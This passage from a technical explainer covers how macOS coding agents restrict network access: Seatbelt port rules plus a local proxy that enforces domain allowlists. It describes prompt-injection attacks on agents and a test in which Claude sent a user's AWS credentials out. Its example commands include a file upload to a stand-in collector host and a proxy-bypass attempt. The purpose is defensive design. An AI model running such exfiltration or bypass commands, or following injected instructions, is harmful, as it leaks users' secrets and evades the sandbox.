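# Seatbelt network rules and proxy-based domain allowlists for coding agents on macOS

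## What happens when a coding agent's command connects to a website?

A coding agent is a program in which a language model writes code and runs commands on the user's machine. Examples include Anthropic's Claude Code, OpenAI's Codex CLI and the code editor Cursor. Most of the commands are ones a programmer would type to run tests, install a library or fetch a page. On macOS, these agents can run commands inside Seatbelt, the operating system's built-in sandbox. Seatbelt's kernel component allows or denies the operations a sandboxed process attempts.

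Seatbelt can restrict connections by address and port, but not by internet domain, such as github.com, which is what people want to use in rules. Agent developers therefore use Seatbelt to let a command connect only to a local proxy, a program that runs outside the sandbox on the same Mac and makes connections on the command's behalf. The proxy checks each requested domain against a domain allowlist, the list of domains it will connect to. How well this works depends on which part of the system receives the destination's name, and when.

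### One command, step by step

Suppose the agent runs `curl https://pypi.org`. curl is a command-line program that transfers data to and from URLs, and pypi.org is the domain name of the Python Package Index, the public collection from which Python programmers install libraries. Machines on the internet find each other by IP address, such as 203.0.113.7 in the older version of the Internet Protocol (IPv4) or 2001:db8::7 in the newer one (IPv6). To connect, curl needs the IP address for pypi.org.

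curl gets a website's numeric address from DNS, the Domain Name System, which Everything curl's *Networking simplified* describes as in effect a big lookup table from names to addresses. The server that answers the query is called a resolver. On a Mac, an ordinary program usually passes the name to mDNSResponder, a system service that queries the resolver for it. According to *chart* (2025), a flow chart with notes by curl's lead developer, curl can skip the lookup if the URL already contains a numeric address, if curl has a connection open to the same host name, or if the answer is in curl's own cache, which typically keeps entries for a minute. Otherwise, curl looks for three kinds of DNS record. A records hold IPv4 addresses, AAAA records hold IPv6 addresses, and an HTTPS record can hold other facts about the server, such as the HTTP versions it supports.

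curl also needs a port, a number that marks out one service on a machine, so that a web server and a mail server can share an address. HTTPS uses port 443 by default and plain HTTP uses port 80. curl passes the address and the port to the kernel, the core of the operating system, and requests a connection. The name plays no part in this request. The kernel receives something like "203.0.113.7, port 443", and nothing in that pair records that curl started from pypi.org.

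One URL can produce several such requests. According to *chart*, curl may race up to four kinds of connection attempt, starting each a little after the one before: QUIC (a newer transport that runs over UDP) on IPv6, QUIC on IPv4, then the older transport, TCP, on IPv6 and on IPv4. curl keeps the first connection that succeeds and drops the rest.

Once a TCP connection is open, curl and the server perform a TLS handshake to agree on keys for encrypting everything that follows. (QUIC builds the handshake into the connection itself.) curl's opening message normally includes the host name in the Server Name Indication (SNI) field, which a server hosting many sites at one address uses to choose the right certificate. *TLS Encrypted Client Hello* (Rescorla, Oku and colleagues, 2026) calls this field perhaps the most sensitive information that TLS 1.3 leaves unencrypted. The standard lets a client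 hide the name by encrypting the real opening message under a key that the server's operator publishes, then wrapping it in a public message with innocuous values in the sensitive fields. An observer may still learn the domain from an unencrypted DNS query, or guess it from the server's address.

Finally, curl sends the HTTP request over the encrypted connection, including the path, the headers and any data. If one command downloads a package and another uploads a private key to the same host, their contents differ at this step.

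A forward proxy, which makes connections for its clients, changes the order. For coding agents, the proxy runs on the same Mac, and commands reach it over loopback, the addresses a machine uses to reach itself (chiefly 127.0.0.1 and ::1, usually called localhost). curl no longer needs to look up pypi.org, because it connects to the proxy's loopback port and passes along the name. The proxy then resolves the name and connects to the site. According to Anthropic's current documentation, Claude Code's proxy checks the host name against the allowlist before resolving it.

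| Step | Kernel, when curl makes the request | DNS resolver | Local proxy, if curl uses one | Web server |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Name lookup | A message to a system service or a resolver | The domain | The domain, since the proxy starts the lookup | Nothing |
| Connection | An IP address and port; with a proxy, only the proxy's own loopback address and port | Nothing | The domain and port that curl requests | The address from which the connection comes |
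| Start of TLS | Bytes on an open connection | Nothing | The SNI, if the proxy reads it and the client has not encrypted it | The SNI |
| HTTP request | Encrypted bytes | Nothing | Encrypted bytes, unless the proxy performs TLS termination | The path, headers and data |

TLS termination, in the last row, means the proxy decrypts the traffic using a certificate the client trusts, so it can read the requests. Claude Code's proxy does not do this by default. It allows or blocks each connection based on the host name the client supplies, then relays the allowed traffic without being able to read it.

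### Seatbelt in outline

Seatbelt is an informal name for the interface that Apple documents as sandbox(7), according to Chromium's *The Mac Sandbox*. A sandbox profile is a set of rules, written in a Scheme-like language, for what a process may do. According to Apple's *SANDBOX-EXEC(1)*, the deprecated command-line tool `sandbox-exec` runs a command in a sandbox with a given profile. The process cannot then remove its sandbox, and an operation that breaks a rule fails with the error "operation not permitted", as *sandboxing on macos* explains. New processes inherit their parent's sandbox, so if a confined shell starts Python and Python starts curl, the same rules apply to all three. Apple's *SANDBOX(7)* (2010) adds that the system generally enforces restrictions only when a process acquires a resource, so a program that already has a file open for writing may keep writing to it. For a network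 connection, the comparable moment is when the process asks to connect, and the kernel has an address and a port to check against the rules.

### Why restrict an agent's outbound traffic?

A programmer's own terminal usually has no such limits. An agent is different because it acts on what it reads, and much of that comes from strangers. Prompt injection is text in that material written to make the agent follow someone else's instructions. Anthropic's 2026 post *How we contain Claude across products* describes how a connector to GitHub, the code-hosting site, may pass every malware check and still load a README file (a software project's introductory page) containing a prompt injection into the model's context.

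An agent that follows such instructions can steal many kinds of credentials. By default, Claude Code's sandbox lets commands read almost the whole disk. An earlier edition of Anthropic's documentation page *Configure the sandboxed Bash tool* lists `~/.aws/credentials` (keys to an Amazon cloud account) and `~/.ssh/` (keys for logging in to other machines) among the readable files. The current edition describes the same default and adds that Claude Code has no built-in list of credentials to protect, so users have to name the files and variables themselves. Developers also often keep access tokens in environment variables, which are named values that a process passes on to the programs it starts. Claude Code inherits all of these variables from the terminal session, according to *Sandboxing agentic coding tools is a networking problem*, a blog post by Formal, which sells access-control software.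 Claude Code can also read the `.env` files in a project directory, where many projects keep passwords, even if the developer has told Git to ignore them.

Incoming traffic can carry hostile code. An injected instruction can make the agent download malware, and a library from a public registry can contain malware without any injection. Anthropic treats every outside resource as a possible source of both hostile code and prompt injection. It notes that the usual precautions for software dependencies, such as pinning versions and verifying signatures, address hostile code but not prompt injection.

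Formal uses the programmer Simon Willison's concept of the "lethal trifecta", the combination of untrusted content, sensitive data and a means of communicating with the outside. A coding agent on a real project has the first two almost by definition, so the practical thing to restrict is its means of communication.

Another approach is to train the model to refuse, and Anthropic reports progress. On a prompt-injection benchmark from Gray Swan, a company that tests AI systems, attacks on Claude Opus 4.7 succeeded about 0.1% of the time on a single attempt, but around 5–6% of the time when the attacker had 100 attempts and could adapt. An attacker who can plant text in many places may well get 100 attempts.

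In a controlled test that Anthropic ran on itself in February 2026, a researcher emailed an employee a prompt that looked like routine set-up instructions, and the employee launched Claude Code with it. One step was to read `~/.aws/credentials`, encode the contents and send them to an outside address. Claude completed the theft in 24 of 25 runs. Every run used the same well-made prompt, so the result is weak evidence of how often attacks succeed in general. The instruction also came from the user, whereas prompt injection more commonly hides in a file or web page, and Anthropic's defences in the model rely heavily on what the user appears to want. The company concluded that only limits outside the model could have stopped the theft: network controls that block the upload whatever the intent behind it, and file rules that keep the credentials out of reach.

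Nor does the danger require an attacker. The same post mentions Claude models that "helpfully" escaped a sandbox in order to finish a task.

### Why file limits and network limits depend on each other

Claude Code's first safeguard was to ask the user's permission before running most commands. By Anthropic's count, users approved roughly 93% of these requests, and they paid less attention to each one as the number grew. A sandbox makes most of the requests unnecessary because commands that stay inside its boundary can run without permission. Anthropic's *Beyond permission prompts* (2025), the October post that introduced the sandbox, reports an 84% reduction in requests.

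That figure is self-reported from the company's "internal usage", and the post does not give the number of users, the period or the counting method. It measures interruptions and does not show how many attacks the sandbox would stop. If it is roughly right, most of the commands that once waited for a person's approval now run with only the sandbox to contain them, so a hole in the sandbox is more dangerous than before.

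The October post argues that the boundary has to cover both files and the network. A compromised agent with open network access can send out sensitive files such as SSH keys, and if the file system is open, it can escape the sandbox and regain network access.

Anthropic's current documentation explains how a command can escape through the file system. A confined command with free write access can alter a shell startup file, a program that other commands call, or Claude Code's own settings. When something outside the sandbox later runs or reads the altered file, the restriction no longer applies, and the attacker has not had to defeat the kernel or the proxy. Claude Code lets users turn off file isolation and keep the network limits, but the documentation recommends this only for workloads that the user trusts not to widen their own access. A project's own settings file cannot turn off file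 isolation.

Stricter file rules would reduce the risk of an open network but not remove it. A user could forbid commands to read any credentials, which would leave fewer keys to send out. But a command has to read the project it is working on, which may be confidential, and an open network would still let it fetch hostile code.

Anthropic has become more cautious about what combining filesystem and network isolation achieves. Its October post said that "even a successful prompt injection is fully isolated", while the current documentation says sandboxing reduces risk but "is not a complete isolation boundary". By default, Claude Code lets commands write only to the working directory, a temporary directory and any directories the user has added, but they can read nearly every file, including credentials. Unless the user has tightened those read rules, the network rules are almost the only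 protection against a command sending a stolen key off the machine.

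## Why can a Seatbelt profile not name a domain?

A Seatbelt profile can't name a domain for two reasons. A request to connect carries no domain name, as in the curl example, and the profile language apparently accepts only `localhost` (this Mac) or `*` (any machine) as the host in a network rule. A profile can therefore separate this Mac from all other machines and pick out ports, but it can't single out an IP address such as 203.0.113.7 or a domain such as pypi.org.

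### What the kernel receives

To open a connection, a program passes the kernel a socket, which is the program's end of the connection, and a short data structure containing the address and port. The structure has no field for a name. It holds a port number and a 32-bit address for IPv4, or a port number, a 128-bit address and two other numeric values for IPv6.

Seatbelt checks the request through the TrustedBSD mandatory access control framework, which places hooks in the kernel where a security module can refuse an operation before it runs. "Mandatory" means the process cannot opt out. HackTricks' *macOS Sandbox*, a reference for security testers, describes hooks on system calls throughout the kernel.

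In *Apple's Sandbox Guide*, the reverse engineer fG! (2011) tried to trace every Seatbelt operation to the kernel functions that check it in Mac OS X 10.6.8. For outbound traffic, the guide lists the functions for connecting, sending and writing to a socket. The check on sending matters for UDP because a program can send a UDP packet without connecting first. For inbound traffic, the guide lists the functions for listening, receiving and reading. A separate check applies when a program binds a socket, which means claiming a local address and port.

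fG! tested a profile that denied TCP connections to any remote host. Under that profile, the command `telnet www.google.com 80` printed "Trying 74.125.39.147..." and then failed with "Operation not permitted". The name lookup had succeeded before the sandbox refused the connection. The log entry lists the program, its process number, the denied operation and `74.125.39.147:80`, but not the name www.google.com.

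The kernel also cannot reliably determine the domain from the address. DNS has reverse records that map addresses to names, but whoever controls the address writes them, and for a site on rented servers they often name the hosting company. The SNI field is sent only after the connection is open, which is too late for a check on opening it. fG! also found a check on writes to a socket, but the profile language has no filter for the bytes a program writes.

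A more flexible system than Seatbelt would have the same problem. *AgentBouncer* (Joos and Pradel, 2026) describes a Linux system that intercepts the system calls made by a coding agent's tools and holds each one until it reaches a decision. If no preset rule or earlier decision applies, a language model decides based on the user's task, the agent's stated reason for running the tool, and the tool call itself. The model has far more context than a fixed profile, but Joos and Pradel argue that this is still too little to judge a `connect` call. Installing a package from a registry and sending stolen data to an attacker both appear as a connection to some IP address on port 443.

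AgentBouncer instead judges requests at a proxy, and allows direct connections only to loopback and to that proxy. The proxy decrypts TLS, so the model can use the method, URL and body to judge an HTTPS request. For other TCP traffic sent through the proxy, it has only the destination host and port. In a test with 340 attacks, AgentBouncer reduced the attack success rate from 99.41% to 10.59%. Those attacks included file deletion and other local damage, so the figure doesn't measure the network design alone. The argument about `connect` rests on what the call contains, not on this result.

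### How a profile describes network access

Seatbelt has three main network operations. `network-outbound` covers connecting and sending, `network-inbound` covers accepting and receiving traffic, and `network-bind` covers claiming a local address and port. The name `network*` stands for all of them. A rule combines `allow` or `deny` with an operation and, usually, one or more filters that say which connections it applies to:

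```
(version 1)
(deny default)
(allow network-outbound (remote tcp "*:443"))
(allow network-bind     (local tcp "localhost:8080"))
(allow network-inbound  (local tcp "localhost:8080"))
```

These rules would let a program connect to port 443 on any machine and run a test server on its own port 8080. A working profile also needs rules for files and processes, or the program will not start. `local` means the program's own end of a connection, and `remote` means the other end, even if that is a server on the same Mac.

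The protocol follows `remote` or `local` and can be `ip`, `tcp` or `udp`. Adding a 4 or 6 to the end, as in `tcp4`, limits the rule to that version of the Internet Protocol. According to fG!, both `ip` and `udp` also cover ICMP, the protocol that `ping` uses. A string with a host and a port comes next. If the profile omits it, Seatbelt assumes `*:*`, so Trail of Bits' *seatbelt sandboxer*, a set of instructions for writing profiles, gives `(remote tcp)` as the filter for outbound TCP to any host.

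| Filter | What it matches |
|---|---|
| `(remote tcp)` | TCP to any port on any machine |
| `(remote tcp "*:443")` | TCP to port 443 on any machine |
| `(remote ip "localhost:*")` | Any port on this Mac |
| `(local udp "*:500")` | UDP on the program's own port 500 |
| `(remote unix-socket (path-literal "/private/var/run/syslog"))` | One Unix socket on this Mac |

A Unix socket, in the last row, is a channel between programs on the same machine. It has a file path instead of an address and port, so a profile can name one exactly. Seatbelt rules can also cover a single file, a directory or every path that fits a pattern, but they can't specify remote machines this precisely.

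Accounts differ on which rule wins when two match. According to fG!, Seatbelt stopped at the first match. According to North Pole Security's *Sandbox Rules* (2026), the documentation for a Mac security product, the last match wins. Current software such as the sandboxing library *landstrip 0.8.6* also relies on the newer, last-match behaviour. landstrip writes `(deny network*)` before its exceptions for particular Unix sockets, which would never take effect if the first match won. Rule order matters for any profile that blocks the network and then opens one port.

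### Does the host have to be `*` or `localhost`?

According to fG!, those were the only valid values on 10.6.8, "meaning that you can only filter by port". That was fifteen years ago, and Apple treats the profile language as a private interface that it may change without notice, so no official reference describes what current versions accept. Developers still rely on the old guide. For example, the source code of *nono 0.38.0*, another sandboxing library, cites it as a reference for Apple's private sandbox functions.

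More recent evidence comes from MXC, Microsoft's early-preview system for running untrusted code on Windows, Linux and macOS. A bug report about the sandbox in GitHub's Copilot command-line agent, *Docs present local sandbox capabilities (per-host filtering, cross-platform isolation) as working*, quotes a comment from the MXC source code: "Seatbelt only accepts * or localhost in (remote ...) filters". The comment does not give a macOS version, but it is consistent with fG!'s account, and Microsoft's developers had good reason to find out because they were trying to implement a list of allowed hosts.

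North Pole's documentation suggests that a profile can name a domain. Users of its profile-building form can enter an extra destination such as `example.com:993`, which the product copies into the profile verbatim. That doesn't mean macOS will accept the resulting profile. North Pole also explains that if a profile is invalid, `sandbox_init`, the function that applies it, fails and the program does not run. So if fG! and Microsoft are right, a program whose profile named a domain would fail to start. Even if some version of macOS did accept the name, something would have to convert it to addresses before the kernel could compare it with a connection, so the rule would have all the problems of an IP allowlist.

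According to the bug report, MXC, which offers domain rules on top of Seatbelt, responded to a list of allowed hosts on macOS by allowing all outbound traffic. The source comment describes this as a "best-effort" measure. MXC's macOS code rejected a list of blocked hosts outright. On Linux, with general outbound access switched off, MXC ignored the list of allowed hosts, so even those hosts were unreachable. The macOS behaviour is the dangerous one, because a user who tried to narrow the agent's access would have opened it completely without any warning.

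Microsoft lists MXC's Seatbelt support as experimental and warns against treating any MXC profile as a security boundary yet. It also says MXC does not support proxies on macOS. MXC therefore has no component there that could apply a host list, and the safe choice would have been to reject the setting.

Port rules are still useful on their own. By default, navikt's *cplt*, a sandbox for coding agents, allows outbound connections only on port 443 and blocks connections to services on the same Mac. This stops a command from logging in to another machine over SSH, which normally uses port 22, or querying a database that the developer is running locally. But anyone can run a server on port 443, so the Seatbelt rule that allows a connection to the Python Package Index also allows one to an attacker's server. cplt therefore uses a proxy to filter connections by domain.

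The most valuable rule that the language can express is probably the one that confines a program to this Mac. Gas Town's *macOS sandbox-exec Research Report* (2026), written for a tool that runs coding agents, gives a version of it:

```
(allow network* (local ip "localhost:*"))
(allow network* (remote ip "localhost:*"))
(allow network* (remote unix-socket))
```

Gas Town reports that loopback-only rules work reliably, based on local tests on macOS Sequoia, but the published test does not fully support that claim. With everything denied by default, curl failed to reach an outside host and returned exit code 6, which means it could not resolve the host name. It probably never tried to connect. fG!'s telnet test is much older, but it is better evidence that the kernel refuses the connection itself.

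### What Apple's own profiles do

Apple has published many of the profiles that it uses for parts of macOS, and they offer a check on how its own engineers write network rules. One is for a process of WebKit, the browser engine behind Safari, with a copyright notice for 2013–2016. It denies everything by default and then, for the network, contains this rule:

```
(allow network-outbound
    (literal "/private/var/run/mDNSResponder")
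    (remote tcp))
```

The first filter matches the Unix socket of the system's name resolver by its exact path. The second allows TCP to every port on every machine, which Apple describes in a comment in the file as "arbitrary outbound TCP". A later rule in the same profile allows all outbound UDP.

Another profile covers racoon, a background program that negotiates keys for IPsec, a type of virtual private network. Its network rule includes `(local udp "*:500" "*:4500")` and `(remote udp "*:*")`. Apple lists ports 500 and 4500 for the program's own end of the connection because IPsec key exchange uses them. For the other end, Apple allows UDP to any port on any host.

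Both profiles are consistent with the restriction to `*` and `localhost`, but neither proves it, because these programs might have had open host rules even if the language had allowed narrower ones. A browser has to reach whatever site the user types in, and Apple ships the same IPsec profile to many customers and cannot know in advance which server each will use.

Fulgham (2020), in *[macOS] Remove remote tcp capability from WebContent Sandbox*, later proposed that WebKit stop allowing the process that handles web content to open remote TCP connections. WebKit's developers had by then moved nearly all network activity out of that process, so it no longer needed the permission. The process, which is the part of the browser most exposed to hostile pages, lost its direct access to the network, but the browser could still load any site. The local proxies of coding agents divide the work in much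 the same way.

### Would a list of IP addresses work instead?

Seatbelt does not accept individual addresses. With a filter that does, a developer could look up each approved domain and allow the addresses that come back.

Anthropic has published a firewall that works this way as part of the Claude Code dev container, a ready-made Linux environment for running the agent. When the container starts, a script looks up each approved domain, stores the IPv4 addresses in a table and configures the Linux packet filter to block traffic to other destinations, with a few exceptions such as DNS. For GitHub, the script downloads the published address ranges. It does not repeat the lookups while the container is running.

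An address allowlist has an advantage over a proxy that programs can ignore, because the kernel enforces the allowlist on every program in the container. It also blocks the simplest kind of data theft, in which a command sends data to a server that the attacker has rented at an unrelated address. But domains and addresses do not correspond closely enough for an address allowlist to replace a domain allowlist.

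One reason is that a domain's addresses change, as some unrelated examples in fG!'s guide show. In a log from 2 September, www.google.com is at 74.125.39.147 around 11 in the morning, at 74.125.39.99 shortly after 9 in the evening, and at 74.125.39.106 an hour and a quarter later. In another example, which is undated, it is at 209.85.148.106. A lookup often returns several addresses, so a firewall that stored every answer in the morning might also have had the evening's addresses, but it would have been less likely to have the one from a different range. When an approved site moves to an address outside the stored list, the agent's downloads start to fail, although nothing is wrong with the site or the user's settings.

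More frequent lookups would reduce the problem but not remove it. Large services return different addresses to different resolvers, or rotate them, so the firewall and the command can look up the same name within seconds and get different addresses. To prevent this, the firewall would have to pass its lookup results to the command, or allow each address before the command tried to use it.

*sboxd 0.1.7*, a tool that runs package installers in containers, looks up the approved names once, when it plans the run. It writes the addresses into the container's hosts file, a local table that programs consult before DNS, so the command and the list use the same addresses. It also points the container's DNS settings at 192.0.2.1, where no resolver will answer, so lookups for other names time out. This controls which names a program can resolve, but by itself it doesn't stop a program from connecting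 to a numeric address it already has.

Shared hosting causes the opposite error, letting too much through. A hosting company or content delivery network can serve thousands of unrelated sites from one address. If one of those sites is on the allowlist, an address filter permits connections to all the others. An attacker may be able to open an account with the same provider and receive stolen data at an address the user has approved. Allowing a provider's whole published range makes failures less likely but also lets a command reach more services.

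There is also no good way to convert a rule such as `*.npmjs.org` into IP addresses, because ordinary clients can use DNS to look up particular names but not to list every name under a domain. Building an IP allowlist would require knowing all those names beforehand, whereas a proxy can compare each requested name with the pattern as it arrives.

### Why not use another macOS filter?

macOS has other ways to control network traffic, and some of them can do things that Seatbelt cannot. pf, a packet filter that originated in the OpenBSD operating system, can allow or block individual IP addresses. A pf rule can even contain a host name. But pf looks the name up when it loads the rules, and the administrator has to reload them to pick up a new address, so the result is another IP allowlist.

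pf is also awkward to apply to a single agent. Changing its rules requires administrator rights, and the rules cover the whole machine. They can select traffic by the user account that owns a socket, but not by process. A developer who runs an agent under her own account could not use pf to limit the agent without also limiting her browser. She could give the agent a separate account, at the cost of arranging access to her files and tools.

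Apple's Network Extension framework comes closer than Seatbelt to filtering by domain. A developer can use it to build a content filter, which allows or drops each new connection, or a transparent proxy, which takes over connections even if the program ignores proxy settings. When a program connects through Apple's higher-level networking interfaces, macOS can pass the requested host name to the extension. Many command-line tools instead look up the name themselves and then call `connect` with an address, so the extension has no host name unless it reads the SNI from the traffic.

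The larger obstacle is installation. The developer needs an entitlement, a permission that Apple authorises and the developer includes in the program's code signature. The extension has to come inside an app, and the user has to approve it in System Settings. On a company Mac, the IT department may make that decision. Because the extension can receive traffic from the whole machine, it also has to identify which connections come from the agent, including those from programs that the agent's commands started. This may be worthwhile for a firewall product, but it is a lot to ask of someone who wants to try a command-line tool.

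Gas Town rejects two further options for similar reasons. App Sandbox, which Apple requires for Mac App Store apps, needs an app bundle and signed entitlements, so it cannot confine the arbitrary commands an agent runs. Endpoint Security, a framework for products such as antivirus software, needs a system extension and an entitlement from Apple. Gas Town concludes that `sandbox-exec` is the only practical choice for command-line tools. The comparison leaves out pf and Network Extension, but they need administrator rights or user approval, which counts against them too. `sandbox-exec` is already on every Mac, works without administrator rights, and lets an agent apply a different profile to each command.

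## How does a local proxy turn a port rule into a domain allowlist?

Seatbelt can limit a command's network connections to a single port on the same Mac. A coding agent turns this limit into a domain allowlist by running a proxy on that port, so that a command has to give the proxy a site's domain before it can reach the internet.

### Setting up the sandbox

The agent takes four steps:

1. It starts a proxy outside the sandbox, on a loopback port.
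2. It writes a sandbox profile that denies outbound traffic except to that port.
3. It sets environment variables that contain the proxy's address.
4. It launches the command under the profile.

The proxy is set up first because the Seatbelt profile has to contain its port. OpenAI's *codex-network-proxy* (2026), the documentation for the proxy in Codex, describes two listeners. By default, an HTTP proxy listens on 127.0.0.1:3128, and a SOCKS5 proxy, which can carry any kind of TCP connection, listens on 127.0.0.1:8081. Both stay on loopback unless the user explicitly chooses otherwise, because a wider address could let other machines on the network use them.

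The profile can be very short. Zhao (2026), in *Aegis OS*, describes a system for running coding agents that generates these network rules, among others for files and credentials:

```
(version 1)
(allow default)
(deny network-outbound)
(allow network-outbound (remote ip "localhost:51691"))
```

The first line gives the version of the profile language. `(allow default)` permits everything that no later rule denies, so a real profile needs further rules to protect files. `(deny network-outbound)` blocks all outgoing connections, including those to Unix sockets such as the one for mDNSResponder. The last line allows connections to port 51691 on this Mac, where the proxy is listening. Seatbelt applies the last matching rule, so putting the denial last would block the proxy's port too.

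These rules do not cover `network-inbound` or `network-bind`, so a command could still open a port and listen for connections. Codex is stricter and only adds rules that allow listening if the user has enabled local binding.

The host in the exception has to be written as `localhost`. According to a developer's comment in *koda-sandbox*, the sandboxing code of another coding agent, `sandbox-exec` rejects the entire profile if the rule contains 127.0.0.1, with the error "host must be * or localhost in network address". The project's early tests only searched the profile for the expected text, so the developers didn't find the mistake until a later test ran `sandbox-exec` itself. *koda-sandbox* gives no macOS version, but its code borrows from Gemini CLI, Google's coding agent, so it is far more recent than fG!'s account of the same restriction. The comment also says that `localhost` covers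 both 127.0.0.1 and ::1, so one rule is enough.

Programs find the proxy through environment variables. For Codex's default ports, OpenAI sets `HTTP_PROXY` and `HTTPS_PROXY` to `http://127.0.0.1:3128` and `ALL_PROXY` to the SOCKS5 listener at `socks5h://127.0.0.1:8081`.

`HTTPS_PROXY` sets the proxy for requests to HTTPS sites. Its value begins with `http://` because the client uses plain HTTP to ask the proxy for a connection. The "h" in `socks5h` means that the proxy, not the client, looks up the hostname.

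Another variable, `NO_PROXY`, lists destinations that programs should contact directly. Direct connections usually fail inside the sandbox, so listing a destination here can break a command. In April 2026, OpenAI removed domain suffixes from the `NO_PROXY` value that Codex sets, because the suffixes could make programs look up internal names themselves instead of sending them to the proxy. The list still contains private address ranges.

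Finally, the agent launches the command:

```
/usr/bin/sandbox-exec -p "$PROFILE" -- curl https://pypi.org
```

`$PROFILE` stands for the text of the profile. The full path to `sandbox-exec` keeps the shell from running an attacker's program of the same name from a directory it searches first. A comment in *zerobox-sandboxing*, a library derived from Codex's code, gives the same reason for using the full path. Passing the profile as text avoids a temporary file that another process might alter before `sandbox-exec` reads it. Any programs that curl starts inherit the sandbox, and they also inherit the proxy variables unless something changes them.

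### How the proxy receives the name

For an HTTPS site, curl uses HTTP CONNECT, a request that asks an HTTP proxy to open a tunnel to a host and port. After connecting to 127.0.0.1:3128, curl sends the following text and a blank line:

```
CONNECT pypi.org:443 HTTP/1.1
Host: pypi.org:443
```

If the proxy permits the connection, it looks up pypi.org, connects to port 443 and replies:

```
HTTP/1.1 200 Connection established
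```

From then on, the proxy copies bytes in both directions. curl does the TLS handshake with pypi.org through the tunnel, so the proxy cannot read the encrypted traffic unless it terminates TLS. It can read the domain name because curl sends the CONNECT request before encryption begins.

Plain HTTP needs no tunnel. The client sends the proxy a request with the full URL, such as `GET http://example.com/file.txt HTTP/1.1`, and the proxy makes the request on its behalf, so it can read the path, headers and content as well as the domain name.

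SOCKS5 does the same job in binary. The client first offers a list of authentication methods and the proxy picks one, which may be none at all. The client then sends its request. For pypi.org, the bytes are:

| Bytes, in hexadecimal | Meaning |
|---|---|
| `05` | SOCKS version 5 |
| `01` | Open a TCP connection |
| `00` | Reserved |
| `03` | The destination is a domain name |
| `08` | The name is 8 bytes long |
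| `70 79 70 69 2e 6f 72 67` | pypi.org |
| `01 bb` | Port 443 |

The second byte of the reply is `00` if the connection succeeded, or `02` if the proxy's rules forbid it. Once the proxy has connected, the client can use any protocol that runs over TCP, including SSH. A client can also send a numeric address, marked `01` for IPv4 or `04` for IPv6, and the proxy then receives no domain name.

With both protocols, the client sends the proxy the host name, which a `connect` call does not include.

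A hostile program gains very little by giving the proxy a false domain name, because the proxy looks up the name and makes the outside connection itself. If malware asks for pypi.org to try to reach an attacker's server, the proxy connects to the address it finds for pypi.org, and the malware can't substitute another. The malware could still gain something if pypi.org shared a server with other sites, or if an attacker controlled the DNS answers that the proxy receives.

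### How the proxy decides

The following pseudocode combines OpenAI's published rules with Claude Code's order of checks, in which the proxy checks the list before it looks up the name. It assumes the user has left local and private destinations blocked, which is the default in Codex.

```
function handle(host, port):
    name = normalise(host)       # lower case, no final dot

    if a deny rule matches name:
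        refuse "blocked-by-denylist"

    if name is localhost or a private address:
        if no allow rule lists it exactly:
            refuse
        connect to name on port, and stop

    if no allow rule matches name:
        if neither the user nor an earlier approval permits it:
            refuse "blocked-by-allowlist"

    addresses = look up name
    if the lookup fails or finds a private address:
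        refuse
    connect to one of addresses on port
```

The proxy has to normalise the name because DNS ignores case and accepts a final dot, so `PyPI.org.` and `pypi.org` are the same domain. If the proxy compared the raw text, a command could get around a rule against `evil.example` by requesting `EVIL.example`.

The proxy then compares the name with the rules. OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security*, the user documentation for Codex, defines three kinds of pattern:

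| Rule | `example.com` | `api.example.com` | `badexample.com` |
|---|---|---|---|
| `example.com` | Match | No match | No match |
| `*.example.com` | No match | Match | No match |
| `**.example.com` | Match | Match | No match |

A user who allows `*.pypi.org` instead of `**.pypi.org` has not allowed pypi.org itself, so `curl https://pypi.org` will fail. The dot after the asterisks matters too, because if the proxy only checked whether a name ended in "example.com", anyone could register badexample.com and receive data there.

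Codex's domain rules do not include a port, so allowing a host for HTTPS also seems to allow its other ports, including port 22 for SSH, if the program can use the SOCKS5 proxy.

In the proxy's domain list, a denial always overrides a permission, regardless of their order or how specific they are. A user can allow `**.example.com` and deny `uploads.example.com`, which leaves the rest of the site available. But if the user denies `*.example.com`, no rule can restore `api.example.com`. In a Seatbelt profile, by contrast, a later permission can override an earlier denial.

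OpenAI's two documents differ on a bare `*`, which would match every public host. It is a valid allow rule in the user documentation, which warns that it gives broad access. A comment in the proxy's sample configuration describes it as rejected, but a later passage adds that the proxy accepts it if the calling program has enabled it. Codex presumably enables it for user settings. With this rule in place, only deny rules block public hosts, so an attacker can use any public domain the user has not denied.

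If no rule matches, the proxy can refuse the request or seek approval for it. In Claude Code, a request for a new domain normally triggers a permission prompt, and Anthropic's proxy handles the answer. OpenAI's proxy supports a hook, a function supplied by the program that runs the proxy, which can permit a request that the allowlist would have refused. The hook cannot override an explicit denial or the block on local destinations.

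The hook can also receive the command that made the request, so Codex can treat permission to run a command as permission for its connections. If a user has approved all curl commands for a session, the hook can approve their network requests automatically. OpenAI's sample code does this for any command that begins with `curl `. An agent that copied the sample would let such commands reach every public host that no rule denies, even if the user only meant to avoid being asked about curl again.

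The proxy in the pseudocode looks up a name only after approving it. A refused name never reaches a DNS resolver, which matters because a command could hide stolen data in the name itself. The proxy then checks the addresses, since the owner of an approved domain could point it at a private address, such as a router's. According to OpenAI, Codex blocks names whose lookup fails or times out, and names that resolve to local or private addresses, even if they are on the allowlist. OpenAI calls the check best-effort. If the proxy looks up the name once to check it and again to connect, the answer may change in between.

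When Codex's proxy blocks a request, it returns HTTP status 403 and gives the reason in the `x-proxy-error` header. `blocked-by-allowlist` means that no allow rule matched, and `blocked-by-denylist` means that a deny rule did. To unblock the request, a developer can add an allow rule in the first case but has to remove or change the deny rule in the second. `blocked-by-policy` appears to cover other refusals.

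The remaining code, `blocked-by-method-policy`, belongs to a "limited" mode that permits only GET, HEAD and OPTIONS, the HTTP methods normally used for reading. For HTTPS, the method is inside the encrypted tunnel, and OpenAI gives two accounts of how the proxy handles this. In one, it blocks CONNECT requests unless it can decrypt the traffic. In the other, it lets the tunnel through without checking the method, so limited mode would not prevent an upload to an approved HTTPS site.

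A proxy can also keep a more useful record than the kernel does. fG!'s sandbox log had only an address and port for the blocked connection, while Codex's audit events can include the host name, the decision and the reason. They also mark requests that didn't match the allowlist but were permitted by the hook. OpenAI deliberately leaves out full URLs, paths and queries, which often contain private information.

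### Three requests under one list

Suppose the allowlist contains pypi.org and files.pythonhosted.org, the domain from which Python's installer downloads most packages. No hook or prompt can add to it, and Codex's HTTP proxy is listening on port 3128. An agent runs three commands:

```
curl https://pypi.org/simple/
curl -d @notes.txt https://collector.example/
curl --noproxy '*' https://203.0.113.7/
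```

The `-d @notes.txt` option uploads the contents of a file. `--noproxy '*'` makes curl ignore its proxy settings for every destination.

| Command | Destination that the kernel checks | Destination that the proxy receives | Result |
|---|---|---|---|
| Read the package index | `localhost:3128` | `pypi.org:443` | The proxy connects and returns 200 |
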